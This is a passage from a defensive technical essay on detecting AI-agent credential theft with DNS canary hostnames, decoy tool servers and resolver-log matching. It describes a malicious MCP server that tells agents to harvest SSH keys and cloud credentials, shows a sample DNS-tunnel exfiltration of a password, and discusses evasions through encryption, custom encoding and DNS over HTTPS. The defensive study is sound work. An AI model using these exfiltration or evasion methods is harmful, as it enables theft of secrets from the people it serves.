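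But a live decoy is one more server to secure and update, and a careful thief may recognise it as a fake. It also records nothing when a sandbox permits the DNS lookup but blocks the connection, as in BeyondTrust's test. Most defenders should therefore start with an unused address of their own and add a live decoy only if someone has time to maintain it.

### Where to put it

Attackers' own instructions are a good guide for where to plant the hostname. *Deadbugz* (Fogel, 2026) describes a malicious tool server distributed through public contributions to GitHub projects. It offered harmless text formatting at first, but after three calls it changed the instructions it returned and told the agent to look for SSH keys, AWS credentials, command history and Kubernetes configuration. Three of these targets involve files where a hostname fits naturally. SSH configuration names the machines to log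 in to, command history is full of addresses, and Kubernetes, a system for running containers on many machines, keeps its server's address in a configuration file.

Two other experiments by Ghifiardi suggest that it matters whether the bait is on the agent's path to its target. In the earlier one, a language model had to get at the records in the mock service. A debugging page leaked the real key, while the decoys, a backup file with a canary key and an old internal interface, were elsewhere. In both sessions with decoys, the model took the real key from the debugging page and exported the records in six requests without touching a decoy. In the later one, Ghifiardi replaced the real key on the debugging page with a canary key, and a smaller model used it in 19 of 20 sessions.

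The second result probably overstates how well the bait works, because the task told the model which pages to try and there was no real key left to choose. Removing the leak alone also stopped every export, so the canary added detection but no further protection. Both experiments used keys, and an agent may be less likely to take a hostname. Still, the results are a reason to plant the hostname in a file the agent reads during ordinary work, and to be sceptical of a separate folder called "passwords".

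Bait on the path is also within reach of honest agents. In another of Ghifiardi's runs, a legitimate agent had the correct key in its prompt but used the canary key anyway. The best entries for a DNS canary are therefore ones that software reads without looking up the hostname until someone chooses to use it. Two examples:

```
# in an environment file (.env)
REPORTS_DB_URL=postgres://report_ro:Vw8sTq2m@orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com:5432/orders

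# in a kubeconfig file, as one more cluster
- name: prod-recovery
  cluster:
    server: https://api.n7w2e9rjx4u6bk3s.int.example.com:6443
```

**Database strings and environment files.** An environment file lists settings that a program loads when it starts. Loading the setting above causes no DNS lookup, but a database client that uses it has to look up the hostname. Zeltser also suggests fake addresses for internal services and webhooks (addresses that receive automatic notifications). Before planting the entry, the defender should check that no start-up script tests every address in the file, or the canary will trigger an alert each time the machine restarts. The password in the string should not work on any system.

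**Kubeconfig files.** Thinkst's *A Kubeconfig Canarytoken* (2021) explains that a kubeconfig file holds a cluster's name, the address of its control server and the user's credentials. By default, the usual tool, kubectl, reads it from .kube/config in the user's home directory. The file can list several clusters, but kubectl contacts only the one the user has selected, so a decoy cluster with its own user entry can sit there for years without a lookup. Thinkst also suggests placing such files on build and deployment servers, which often hold real ones. An extra host in an SSH configuration file works much the same way.

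**Tool-server entries.** Many agents find their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting language models to outside services. A configuration file lists the tool servers and their addresses. An attacker may well read this file, but the defender's agent also reads it and typically connects to every listed server at the start of a session. Zeltser's *Build a Decoy MCP Server to Catch AI Agent Attackers* recommends listing the decoy server among the disabled servers in Claude Code's settings, so that the agent does not connect to it.

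Disabling the entry reduces the noise but doesn't end it. In a demonstration in Thinkst's *One for all the models out there!*, company policy had switched off MCP for an agent in the code editor VS Code, but the agent read the configuration file anyway and ran its own commands to contact the server. The two guides give different locations for Claude Code's configuration file, so it is worth checking which one the installed version reads.

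Internal documents, such as a wiki page or a project's README, can mention a planted web address, for example as an administration page. Zeltser calls these the noisiest tokens because people click on links and indexing programs fetch them. A hostname in a plain-text table of servers causes fewer false alarms than a link, though some document viewers turn anything that resembles an address into a link. Files with instructions for agents are a poor choice because an uncompromised agent is supposed to follow them and could trigger the token.

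### Kadam's decoy tool server

A tool server can also hand out the bait. Harshad Sadashiv Kadam, an infrastructure security engineer at the job site Indeed, built one that imitates a portal for access to Kubernetes. Kadam writes in *MCP Kube Trap* that the server can sit behind the same gateway as a company's real tool servers, so an agent finds the real and fake tools together. An agent that asks for access receives a decoy kubeconfig file. Using that file with kubectl triggers a canary and gives the thief no access to a real cluster.

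Thinkst reports that Kadam used its Kubernetes, DNS and web tokens, and that alerts came only once a client started to use what the tools had returned. Kadam's own description differs slightly because it also lists a signed record of the agent retrieving the file. In SC Media's *AI agents are already exploring your network*, Kadam explains that a single call to a decoy tool might come from a misconfigured client, but it is much harder to find an innocent explanation if the client then uses the returned credential.

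This design solves part of the placement problem because the hostname does not exist in any file until an agent asks for it, so no indexer or backup program can come across it earlier. A server that generates a new reply for each request could also put a new label in each reply, so a later lookup would point to a single tool call at a known time.

There is little evidence that it works. Kadam writes in SC Media that in early deployments, automated scanners and AI-driven clients called the decoys within minutes, and no legitimate workflow touched them. In *Teaching AI Agents to Fear the Dark*, Kadam adds that scanners listed the tools quickly and superficially, while AI agents selected particular tools and then went further. Neither account gives counts, so neither shows how many agents that received a planted hostname looked it up. Glama's *Deception Remote MCP Server* describes another of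 Kadam's decoys, a fake internal tool that supposedly lets administrators reset any user's password. Every call to this tool raises an alert, so detection does not depend on the agent looking up a hostname.

### How many decoys to plant

*Caught in the Act(ivation)* gives a formula for the chance that a thief who takes one credential sets off an alert. There are m real credentials and k decoys, and β is the miss rate, the chance that the monitor overlooks a decoy that has leaked:

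P(detect) = k/(m + k) × (1 − β)

The fraction is the chance that the thief picks a decoy, and the second factor is the chance that the monitor notices. With three real credentials, three decoys and a miss rate of 0.1, the chance of detection is 3/6 × 0.9 = 0.45. Nine decoys would raise it to 0.675. Adding more decoys can't raise it above 0.9, and a file with three real databases and dozens of unused ones would look odd.

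For a DNS canary, the thief must also try the stolen hostname. If u is the chance of that, the formula becomes:

P(detect) = k/(m + k) × u × (1 − β)

Here β is the chance that a lookup happens but never produces an alert. If one thief in five tries the hostname, the 0.45 drops to 0.09. Published measurements of u are scarce, and the closest evidence concerns stolen keys. OffSeq's *AI-Native security platform* describes a decoy tool server that researchers left open to the internet from May to July 2026. Of the 24 operators who actively exploited it, 19 hunted for credentials, and three stolen credentials were later used against a live AWS account. So some thieves use what they take, but this doesn't give a value of u for hostnames.

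The formula assumes that the thief picks one credential, with every candidate equally likely. A thief who tries two of the six has an 80% chance of trying at least one decoy, compared with 50% for a single pick. An agent that copies the whole file takes all the decoys, and detection then depends on which addresses the thief tries later.

A thief who can tell the real credentials from the decoys has a much better chance of escaping notice. According to the paper, the fraction can collapse in this case, and the formula is "a simple modeling assumption, not a security theorem". The paper's prototype avoids the problem by keeping real credentials out of the text the model can see. An ordinary coding agent has no such separation. It can search the project for REPORTS_DB_URL, find that no program uses the setting, and conclude that the entry is either obsolete or a trap. The lack of legitimate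 use makes the canary's alert meaningful, but it also gives the thief a clue. Mentioning the setting in a plausible recovery script would make this clue less obvious, as long as nobody runs the script routinely.

Planting more decoys also doesn't help with a fault that affects all of them. For example, if the sandbox's resolver refuses queries for the canary's domain, it refuses them for every planted name.

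### Making the bait look real

Decoys should also look like the entries around them. Weinberg (2026) tried to measure this in *PHANTOM*. The PHANTOM program writes decoy credentials from a profile of the organisation that includes its domain, services, database hosts and cloud region. Weinberg compared these decoys with ones made from generic templates, using eight types of credential for four sample organisations, or 32 decoys per method.

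Each decoy's believability score, from 0 to 1, combined four measures: correct format, fit with the organisation, realistic randomness and human acceptance. PHANTOM's decoys averaged 0.78 and the templates 0.58. Human acceptance was 6% for the templates and 100% for PHANTOM's decoys. Three simulated scanners had a combined 13% chance of detecting a PHANTOM decoy and a 39% chance of detecting a template.

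However, no people took part. The program calculated human acceptance by a rule that gave most weight to the decoy's fit with the organisation, and it counted a decoy as convincing if it scored at least 0.65 in total. The fit score rose when the text contained the organisation's domain and service names, which PHANTOM had been designed to insert. One of the scanners looked for the same names. The comparison therefore mostly confirms that PHANTOM inserts text that scores well under these rules. The published averages are also slightly inconsistent, since applying the paper's stated weights to them gives 0.83 for PHANTOM and 0.43 for the templates.

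PHANTOM's decoy AWS key identifiers have 17 characters after the prefix AKIA, but genuine ones have 16, and PHANTOM's format check misses the error. A thief who counted the characters could discard all the decoy keys.

The advice that a planted hostname should follow the pattern of the real ones nearby is sensible even without good measurements. If the company's databases are called orders-db-01 and billing-db-02, a 25-character random label will stand out. orders-db-07 would look better, but someone scanning for common names might look it up. A reasonable compromise is orders-db-x7k2q9, whose six random characters allow about two billion values, which is enough against a scanner that works from a list of common words.

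## Searching DNS logs for planted secrets

The decoy entry in the environment file above contains a fake password, Vw8sTq2m, next to the canary hostname. If a compromised agent sends that file out through a DNS tunnel, the canary does not trigger, but the defender can still find the password by matching it against resolver logs, even if nobody has reported the tunnel's domain. Haryati and Zychlinski recovered planted secrets from resolver logs this way.

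Resolver-log matching needs a resolver that logs the full name in every query, along with the machine that sent it. It also needs a firewall that stops the agent from using any other resolver. The defender then gives a search program the planted secret in each form it might take in a hostname.

The planted secret should be fake. A defender could also search for real keys, but the search program would then need a copy of every key, which would make it an attractive target for thieves.

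*Information-Based Heavy Hitters for Real-Time DNS Data Exfiltration Detection and Prevention* (2023) warns that offline detectors let substantial amounts of data leave before anyone identifies the attack. The search should therefore run as queries arrive. Even then, a short password will get out before the alert unless the resolver searches each name before forwarding the query and refuses any that match.

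### Finding the password in two queries

Suppose the agent encodes the text pw=Vw8sTq2m in base32, cuts the result into pieces and looks them up under example.net, the attacker's domain. The resolver's log then contains two rows:

| Time | Machine | Name |
|---|---|---|
| 14:07:31 | build-07 | ob3t2.vtxh.example.net |
| 14:07:31 | build-07 | bzvi4.jsnu.example.net |

The search program handles them as follows:

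1. Convert the names to lower case and cut off the registered domain, example.net. This leaves ob3t2.vtxh and bzvi4.jsnu.
2. Remove the dots, which gives ob3t2vtxh and bzvi4jsnu.
3. Join the pieces that came from the same machine and went to the same domain, in order of arrival. The result is ob3t2vtxhbzvi4jsnu.
4. Search this text for the encoded forms of the password. One of them is vtxhbzvi4jsn, and it begins at the sixth character.

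Neither query contains that whole string, so a search of individual names would have missed it. A search also has to account for dots, even when the secret is sent in one query. A 40-character key becomes 64 characters in base32, one more than a DNS label can hold, so the sender has to split it with a dot.

### Hexadecimal and the five forms of base32

*The Base16, Base32, and Base64 Data Encodings* (Josefsson, 2006) defines the usual ways to write arbitrary data with a small set of characters. Hexadecimal, or base16, is the easiest to search for because it turns each byte into two characters, so Vw8sTq2m becomes 567738735471326d whatever comes before it.

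Base32 takes five bytes at a time, which is 40 bits, and writes them as eight characters of five bits each. A byte has eight bits, so four of the eight characters contain parts of two neighbouring bytes. How the password's bits fall into characters depends on where the password starts within a group of five bytes. There are five possible starting places, and each produces a different string:

| Bytes before the password in its group | Characters that stay fixed | Password bits in the character before | Password bits in the character after |
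|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | kz3tq42uoezg | 0 | 4 |
| 1 | lhoodtkryte3 | 2 | 2 |
| 2 | m5zyonkhcmtn | 4 | 0 |
| 3 | vtxhbzvi4jsn | 1 | 3 |
| 4 | wo44hgvdrgjw | 3 | 1 |

The twelve fixed characters encode 60 of the password's 64 bits. The other four bits share characters with the neighbouring data, so the search has to leave out those characters, which change with that data. In the example, the fourth string appeared in the log because "pw=" put three bytes before the password. If the agent had put twelve bytes there instead, the third string would have appeared, because twelve bytes fill two groups of five and leave two over.

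This Python function produces the five strings for any secret:

```python
import base64

def base32_forms(secret: bytes):
    forms = []
    for before in range(5):
        text = base64.b32encode(b"\0" * before + secret).decode()
        first = -(-8 * before // 5)                # round up
        last = 8 * (before + len(secret)) // 5     # round down
        forms.append(text[first:last].lower())
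    return forms
```

It puts zero to four dummy bytes in front of the secret, encodes the result and keeps only the characters made up entirely of the secret's bits. Josefsson defines a second base32 alphabet, which uses 0 to 9 and A to V. This alphabet groups bits the same way, so it adds another five strings.

### Secrets in pieces

Joining queries is the step most likely to go wrong. A program may look up both the IPv4 and IPv6 addresses of a name, which logs the name twice. Counters like those BeyondTrust added to its names interrupt the joined text. Attackers may also use several domains. The Saitama malware, used against the Jordanian government in 2022, rotated among three domains and paused for about a minute on average between queries (Ruffing, Petrov and colleagues, 2025, *Improving the Identification of Real-world Malware's DNS Covert Channels*).

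The order of cutting and encoding matters too. If the agent cuts the password into Vw8s and Tq2m and then encodes each half, it sends kz3tq4y and kryte3i. The joined text contains none of the five strings, but kz3tq4 begins the first string and kryte3 ends the second. Any base32 piece of the secret is also a piece of one of the five strings, apart from a character at either end. The defender can therefore skip the joining and search each name for fragments of the five strings.

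Fragments of six characters are too short for this. Suppose the resolver receives a million queries a day, and each name has about 50 places where a match could start. If the names were random base32 text, six-character fragments of this password would produce one or two false matches a day. A planted secret of 40 characters allows 261 fragments of twelve characters, which under the same assumptions would produce a false match about once in 240,000 years. The planted secret should therefore be long, and it won't look odd because real cloud keys are long too.

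### Why letter case damages base64

Base64 distinguishes capital letters from small ones, so "V" stands for 21 and "v" for 47. DNS ignores this difference (Eastlake, 2006, *Domain Name System (DNS) Case Insensitivity Clarification*).

In base64 the password is Vnc4c1RxMm0, without the equals sign at the end. If a server on the way converts the name to lower case, the attacker receives vnc4c1rxmm0, which decodes with four of the eight bytes wrong. The attacker could try restoring the capitals, but the eight letters allow 256 combinations of upper and lower case, and a longer key allows far more. Even unchanged capitals may cause trouble, since Tom (2017), in *RFC Errata*, reports that some authoritative servers and protective devices silently drop queries that contain them.

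Base64 data can still survive a DNS lookup if every server preserves letter case, as it did for BeyondTrust. The defender should therefore search for base64 too, and loses little by ignoring case. Base64 encodes bytes in groups of three, so the password can take three forms, depending on where it starts within a group. In lower case, the parts of these forms that don't change with the surrounding data are vnc4c1rxmm, z3ohnuctjt and wdzhzvheyb. Together with the plain text, the hexadecimal form and the ten base32 strings, the defender has 15 strings to search for.

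### What the search misses

Searching for a planted password fails if the password is encrypted, because the defender can't predict the encrypted text. *Distributed, Linux Kernel Integrated Security Framework* (Parasnis, 2025) lists several ways to disguise the word TopSecret in a hostname. The hexadecimal and base64 versions are easy to search for. A mask that combines every byte with the same one-byte value has only 255 variants, so a defender could try them all. The defender can't search for the versions encrypted with AES or RC4, two standard ciphers, without the key.

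A custom encoding can defeat this search. One version of the RogueRobin malware that Ruffing and colleagues studied wrote its data in hexadecimal and then replaced the digits with letters using its own scheme. None of the 15 strings would match data encoded this way, although a defender who learned the scheme could add another string for it.

Compression also changes the pattern, because the compressed form of a password depends on the text around it. The defender can undo compression without a key, but only after collecting the pieces, putting them in order and guessing the format. An attacker can instead send one or two characters per query, which leaves no fragment long enough to recognise.

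The search also misses queries that never reach the logged resolver. An agent might contact a public resolver directly, or use DNS over HTTPS, which hides lookups inside encrypted web traffic. *Evasion-Resilient Detection of DNS-over-HTTPS Data Exfiltration* (2025) tested models for detecting data theft in such traffic. The two most sensitive models caught about 99.99% of the malicious traffic in a labelled dataset, but with about 1% false positives. Blocking other resolvers is the better remedy where the operator can do it. Customers of a hosted sandbox may have no access to the resolver's log.

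Finally, the search works only if the agent steals the decoy. If the agent sends out only the real key from the line above, the search finds nothing. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* uses a similar exact search as a "deterministic backstop" for the model's written output, and it too can catch only a decoy that the agent has taken.

### Comparison with anomaly detection

The older approach looks for names that seem unusual, without knowing what the thief has taken. Nadler, Aminov and Shabtai (2017), in *Detection of Malicious and Low Throughput Data Exfiltration Over the DNS Protocol*, grouped queries by registered domain and examined the last six hours of each domain's traffic once an hour. They measured the average length of the names, the number of different names and the share of queries that were not repeats. They also measured the types of record requested, how much of each name an English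 word made up, and the randomness of the characters. The measure of randomness was entropy:

H = −Σ p(x) log₂ p(x)

Here p(x) is the fraction of the name's characters that are x. A name made of one repeated letter has an entropy of zero bits, and a name with 16 equally common characters has an entropy of four bits.

The researchers trained a model on one day of presumably clean traffic from the resolvers of Akamai, an internet infrastructure company. They then added traffic from two tunnelling tools and two simulated pieces of malware to the following days. The model flagged all four, but it also flagged 18 legitimate domains in six days, from traffic that peaked at 47 million queries an hour. Twelve of the 18 belonged to security services, such as antivirus products that look up suspicious items through DNS.

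That false alarm rate is low, but the method discards any domain with fewer than ten subdomains in the six-hour window. Nadler and colleagues estimate that up to 2.5 kilobytes can leave unnoticed in that time, and the two queries in the example carry eleven bytes, far below that limit. They also assumed that the thief uses a single domain with no legitimate purpose. Saitama partly violates this assumption by rotating between domains.

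Newer detectors score well in tests. Tomić, Cvetanović and Tadić (2026), in *Improving DNS Exfiltration Detection via Transformer Pretraining*, trained a language model to read subdomains character by character. It caught 99.3% of malicious names with the alarm threshold set to allow one false alarm per thousand harmless names. Their data came from a Serbian internet provider's log, with traffic from known exfiltration tools added. Each distinct name in the training data appeared about 27 times, so a million similar queries would contain about 37,000 distinct names and cause about 37 false alarms.

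Unlike the 2017 method, this model classifies each name separately, so in principle it could catch a short key. But length and entropy would do little to distinguish the example from other subdomains. As one label, ob3t2vtxhbzvi4jsnu has 18 characters and an entropy of 3.84 bits, while distinct subdomains in the provider's log averaged 33.9 characters and 3.63 bits.

Ruffing and colleagues compared names within groups of 20 queries to the same domain, since ordinary names under one domain tend to resemble each other and encoded data does not. On six test sets, some with tunnelling tools absent from the training data, about 0.2% of harmless groups caused false alarms. The average F1 score, which falls with both missed tunnels and false alarms, was 0.98 out of 1. The method had trouble detecting malware that repeated the same query while waiting for commands, because this looked like normal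 traffic. Content delivery networks, which serve websites from many locations, caused false alarms because the names they generate keep changing. The method's reliance on groups of 20 is also a limitation when a theft takes only two queries, which would not fill a group.

Splunk's *Machine Learning in Security* claims 99.97% accuracy for a commercial detector, measured on traffic into which the company had injected the thefts. All such figures need some caution because, as *Domainator* (2025) notes, earlier research on DNS tunnels barely dealt with traffic from real malware. Nadler, Tomić, Ruffing and their colleagues also didn't test traffic from AI agents, and an agent that installs packages and reads websites may produce unusual patterns of DNS queries.

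A defender can run both an exact search and an anomaly detector on the same log, and each can catch thefts the other misses. An exact search can't find a planted string in an encrypted file, but sending the file takes many long, random-looking names, which an anomaly detector has a good chance of flagging. The exact search works best on a password sent in two short queries.

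## Why a lookup may never reach the defender

Resolver-log matching uses the first server a lookup reaches, while the canary's own alert comes from the last, the authoritative server. Many lookups end between the two, most often because a cache already holds the answer.

### What a cache hides

Suppose the record for a planted name has a TTL of 300 seconds, and build-07, the machine with the decoy file, looks the name up at 12:00. The recursive resolver has no stored answer, so it queries the authoritative server and the defender gets an alert. The resolver may reuse the answer until 12:05. If build-07 looks up the name again at 12:03, it gets the stored answer and the authoritative server receives no query. By 12:06 the answer has expired, so a third lookup causes a new query and another alert.

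Missing the 12:03 lookup costs little here, since the defender already has an alert for this machine. It costs more when someone has planted the same hostname on two machines that share a resolver:

| Time | Event | One name on both machines | A different name on each machine |
|---|---|---|---|
| 12:00 | build-07 looks up its decoy | Defender sees it | Defender sees it |
| 12:03 | build-08 looks up its decoy | Cache hides it | Defender sees it |
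| 12:06 | build-08 tries again | Defender sees it | Cache hides it |

The defender can't tell that a second machine is involved if both machines use the same name. The 12:06 query has the same name as the first and comes from the same resolver, so it looks like build-07 trying again. When each machine has its own name, the cache hides only repeat lookups from the same machine.

A harmless lookup can also hide a theft. If a colleague tested the name at 12:00 and the thief used it at 12:03, the defender would close the first alert as a false alarm and never get a second. This is one reason to test with throwaway names.

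Caching therefore mainly hides repeat lookups and lookups of shared names. No cache can hold an answer for a name that nobody has looked up, so the first lookup of a new name normally reaches the authoritative server, whatever the TTL. The exception is when a resolver can work out the answer from an earlier lookup of a different name.

A lookup may pass through several caches on its way to the defender. *XDRI Attacks* (2022), a study of home routers, describes caches in the operating system, the router and the internet provider's resolver. Together they don't normally hide repeat lookups for longer than a single cache would, because each passes on only the seconds left before the answer expires. But if the machine's own cache answers a lookup, it won't appear in the agent's resolver log either.

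### Shorter TTLs

Setting the TTL to zero should make the 12:03 lookup visible. Under the current definition in *Serving Stale Data to Improve DNS Resiliency* (Lawrence, Kumari and Sood), a resolver may use a zero-TTL answer only for the request in progress and should not store it.

However, some resolvers keep using an answer after its TTL has run out. Bhowmick, Ashiq and colleagues (2023) measured this in *TTL Violation of DNS Resolvers in the Wild*, using a commercial proxy network of home computers. They had each computer fetch a unique hostname, changed the hostname's address after the TTL had run out, and had the same computer fetch it again. A connection to the old address meant that a cache was still using the expired answer. To separate the resolvers from the computers' own caches, they judged a resolver only if at least five computers used it. With a TTL of one minute, 8.74% of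 the resolvers kept answers too long, compared with 6.53% at five minutes and 0.31% at an hour.

This pattern suggests that some operators set a minimum TTL, an option in several popular resolver programs. The study did not test a TTL of zero, but a minimum would probably override that too. The problem was much more common in some countries, such as China, where about 62% of the tested computers used a resolver that extended the TTL. A thief's repeated lookups may therefore stay hidden even when the defender's own resolver respects the TTL. RIPE Labs, which publishes internet measurements, mentions an older report of the same behaviour in the local resolvers of EC2, Amazon's cloud service and a likely place for an agent to run.

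A short TTL won't look suspicious. *XDRI Attacks* found that 14% of the popular domains it measured had TTLs of up to 60 seconds, and 55% had TTLs under five minutes. A TTL of zero may be less common, and Lawrence and colleagues note that it has caused trouble for some software. A TTL of a few seconds works nearly as well, and even the 60-second TTL in the zone above does not delay the first alert.

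### Why query counts don't count uses

Five queries for a planted name could come from one attempt to use it or from fifty. Caches lower the count, and a resolver that receives several requests for the same name at once may combine them into one query.

The number of DNS requests can also rise, because a program may request both the IPv4 and the IPv6 address, and its machine may use several resolvers. Bhowmick and colleagues allowed for up to eight DNS requests per web request because that covered 99.9% of the web requests in their data.

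Large public resolvers can also query again before the TTL runs out. In *Public DNS Resolvers Meet Content Delivery Networks*, Kernan, Li and colleagues (2025) looked up each name once to fill the cache, waited 15 seconds and then looked it up three more times. Google's and OpenDNS's resolvers still had far fewer answers in cache than Cloudflare's, which fits earlier evidence that Google's and OpenDNS's servers share caches less. A repeat lookup at 12:03 through Google's resolver may therefore trigger a second alert. Some resolvers also send part of the client's address to the authoritative server, so that it can give different answers to different networks. Kernan and colleagues cite a study in which this increased public resolvers' queries to one content delivery network eightfold.

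The monitoring software should therefore group the queries for one name into a single incident. The time of the first query is useful evidence, but the number of queries is a poor measure of how often anyone used the name.

### Cached "no such name" answers

If the canary server answers with NXDOMAIN, resolvers cache that answer too. *Negative Caching of DNS Queries (DNS NCACHE)* (Andrews, 1998), the standard on the subject, sets the caching time to the lower of the last field in the zone's SOA record and that record's own TTL. Both are 60 seconds in the zone above. If a defender copied an SOA record with 3600 in both places, repeat lookups would stay hidden for an hour, even with a TTL of zero on every address record. The defender can shorten that time by lowering either number.

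A cached NXDOMAIN also hides more lookups from the defender than an ordinary cached answer because it covers every record type. The wildcard above has only an IPv4 address, so the server answers an IPv6 request with NODATA, which means the name exists but has no record of that type. The resolver caches NODATA for IPv6 only, so a later IPv4 lookup still reaches the server, whereas a cached NXDOMAIN would block lookups of both types.

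Andrews' standard applied a stored NXDOMAIN only to the exact name. Bortzmeyer and Huque (2016), in *NXDOMAIN*, extended it to all names underneath, since a name that doesn't exist can't have anything below it. If a resolver has stored NXDOMAIN for q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com, it should now answer a lookup of orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com from its cache. Resolvers vary in whether they do this, because the rule is a recommendation and the way some of them store names makes it awkward to follow.

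Negative caching can hide a canary's first lookup if somebody tests the zone too early. Before the parent zone has a delegation for int.example.com, its servers answer NXDOMAIN. If the resolver stores that answer for int.example.com itself, it may return NXDOMAIN for every canary in the zone until the answer expires. The parent zone's SOA record sets the expiry time, up to the resolver's own limit, which Andrews suggests setting at one to three hours. The defender can prevent this by setting up the delegation before anyone looks up a name below it.

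### Queries that arrive one label at a time

Many resolvers no longer send the full name to every server. Bortzmeyer, Dolmans and Hoffman (2021), in *DNS Query Name Minimisation to Improve Privacy*, describe a method that sends each server just one label more than the zone it is known to serve. With an empty cache, a lookup of the decoy database's hostname would cause these queries:

| Server | Name in the query |
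|---|---|
| Root | com |
| com | example.com |
| example.com | int.example.com |
| Canary server | q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com |
| Canary server | orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com |

If the canary server answers the fourth query with NXDOMAIN, a resolver that takes this to mean no names exist underneath will not send the fifth. Software that matches only complete planted names would then miss the lookup, but software that compares single labels with the register would still catch it.

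The defender can match a lookup to a canary only if the query that arrives includes the random label. Suppose several canaries shared a word nearest the zone, as in q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.db.int.example.com. The resolver would first query db.int.example.com. If the server replied NXDOMAIN, the log would contain only "db", which matches nothing in the register. The server would then receive no query for any other canary under db through the same resolver until the cached answer expired. Putting the random label directly under the zone, as in the table, avoids this.

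The wildcard also avoids this problem, because it gives an address for every name at every level. Home-made canary software that recognises only complete planted names needs more care, because the correct reply for a name between the zone and a planted name is NODATA. Bortzmeyer and Huque call servers that reply NXDOMAIN in this case "definitely wrong".

The same applies to tokens that carry extra data. Canarytokens puts the encoded data to the left of the token, so shortened queries reach the token first. If a server answered the token itself with NXDOMAIN, it could still raise the alert but might lose the data.

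Shortening queries also affects the count, since the single lookup in the table causes two queries at the canary server. Bortzmeyer and colleagues cite research in which the method increased lookups by up to 26%. Shortening doesn't affect matching against resolver logs, because the agent's recursive resolver still receives the full name.

### Answers derived from a signed wildcard zone

The first lookup of a fresh name can go unseen mainly when a wildcard zone is signed with DNSSEC, an extension that adds digital signatures so that resolvers can check whether an answer is genuine. To prove that a name doesn't exist, the server sends a signed record showing that there are no names between two neighbours in alphabetical order. It sends the same kind of record with a wildcard answer, to show that the zone has no exact record for the name.

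Fujiwara, Kato and Kumari (2017), in *Aggressive Use of DNSSEC-Validated Cache*, recommend that resolvers which check signatures reuse these proofs. Suppose the canary zone is signed, and somebody looks up q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com:

1. The canary server sends the wildcard's address, with proof that no names in the zone come after ns1. The defender gets an alert.
2. Seconds later, a different machine looks up another canary, t6hn3w0pzr5d8yqe.int.example.com, through the same resolver.
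3. This name also comes after ns1, so the resolver already has proof that only the wildcard can match it.
4. The resolver builds the answer from the stored wildcard record and sends no query.

The defender would not see the second lookup, even though nobody had looked up that name before. A canary whose label starts with n7w2 would still cause a query because it comes before ns1, outside the range of that proof. The effect lasts only while the resolver has both the proof and the wildcard record cached, so short TTLs limit it.

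Unbound, an open-source resolver, generates wildcard answers in this way when the operator turns on its aggressive-nsec setting, according to NLnet Labs' *Aggressive NSEC*. A defender can turn the setting off on the agent's resolver but not on the thief's.

Leaving the canary zone unsigned works everywhere, because a resolver may reuse only proofs that it has checked. The company's main domain can remain signed. Removing the wildcard from a signed zone would not help, because an NXDOMAIN answer comes with the same kind of proof and can stop lookups of neighbouring names from reaching the defender. Giving every canary its own record would make the resolver send a query, but a stranger could then learn the names from the signed proofs, since each proof gives the names on either side of a gap.

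### When the canary server is down

If the authoritative server is unreachable, it can't record a lookup, and the outage may be hard to notice because the resolver can still answer. Lawrence and colleagues allow a resolver to keep using an expired answer that it can't refresh, and suggest a limit of one to three days. If a thief returned to a decoy database during an outage, the database client would get the old address and try to connect as before, but the canary server wouldn't log the lookup.

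The same behaviour can make a health check appear to succeed even if the server has been off since yesterday, because a lookup of an old canary name can still return an address. The check has to confirm that a new query appeared in the log.

A TTL of zero prevents stale answers, because a resolver must not store the record, but it can't recover a query the server missed. To catch such queries, the defender needs a second authoritative server on a different network, with its log connected to the same alerts. With only one server, even a brief restart can mean missing several minutes of lookups, since Andrews allows a resolver to treat an unresponsive server as dead for up to five minutes.

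### Lookups that stop inside the network

Security controls can stop a lookup before any server outside the defender's network receives it. Each leaves its record in a different place:

| Where the lookup stops | What happens | Where a record may remain |
|---|---|---|
| Resolver with a list of approved domains | It refuses the planted name | The resolver's query log |
| Security filter | It returns an error or a harmless address | The filter's log of blocked names |
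| Hosts file | The machine takes the address from a local file and sends no query | Monitoring software on the machine |
| Web proxy | It refuses the hostname before looking it up | The proxy's log of refused requests |
| Offline machine | The query gets no reply | Logs on the machine, if someone collects them |

A web proxy can hide a lookup because many programs pass the hostname to the proxy instead of looking it up themselves. The commercial service that Bhowmick and colleagues used looked up and cached names on its own server by default. A proxy that checks its rules before the lookup prevents the leak that Zenity Labs found in Claude's sandbox, but it also prevents the canary's query. The operator should still have the proxy check its rules first, and get the alert from the proxy's log. A database client usually doesn't go through a web proxy, so a decoy connection string may still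 cause a lookup where a decoy web address doesn't.

The simplest remedy for a resolver or filter is an exception for the canary domain. This gives an attacker very little, since any data sent in names under int.example.com goes to the defender's own server. An exception for a hosted service's whole domain is much riskier, because anyone can create a free token at Canarytokens and read the data that arrives with it. A compromised agent could then send secrets to an attacker's token. An exception for a hosted canary should cover only that token's hostname.

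#### Turning refusals into alerts

The operator can also leave the block in place and search the local log for planted labels. Suppose the agent's resolver refuses the decoy database's hostname and records this:

| Time | Machine | Name | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 14:22:10 | build-07 | orders-ro.q4mz81vtk7c0x5hy.int.example.com | REFUSED |

This row is more useful than the authoritative server's because it identifies the machine. But it leads to an alert only if the log includes refused lookups and a program compares the names in the log with the register.

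With Unbound, the settings for such a resolver could look like this:

```
server:
    log-queries: yes
    aggressive-nsec: no
    local-zone: "." refuse
    local-zone: "pypi.org." transparent
    local-zone: "int.example.com." transparent
```

The first setting logs incoming queries with the client's address, including those the resolver then refuses. The third refuses every name by default, and the last two allow a Python package site and the canary domain, in that order. Without the last line, lookups of canary names don't reach the canary server, but the local log still records them.

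If both logs can raise alerts, the software should combine matches for the same label at about the same time into one incident. A match in the local log with no query at the canary server may mean that a filter or cache stopped the lookup, or that the canary server has failed.

A machine normally checks its hosts file before it uses DNS, so neither log will record a lookup that the file answers. Operators sometimes block unwanted domains by copying long lists of them into this file, and a copied list may include the domain of a hosted canary service. The defender should check the file in any image used to start agents. If a sandbox has no network, a small resolver inside it can log every name requested and return an error. This works only if the agent can't edit the log and another system collects it.

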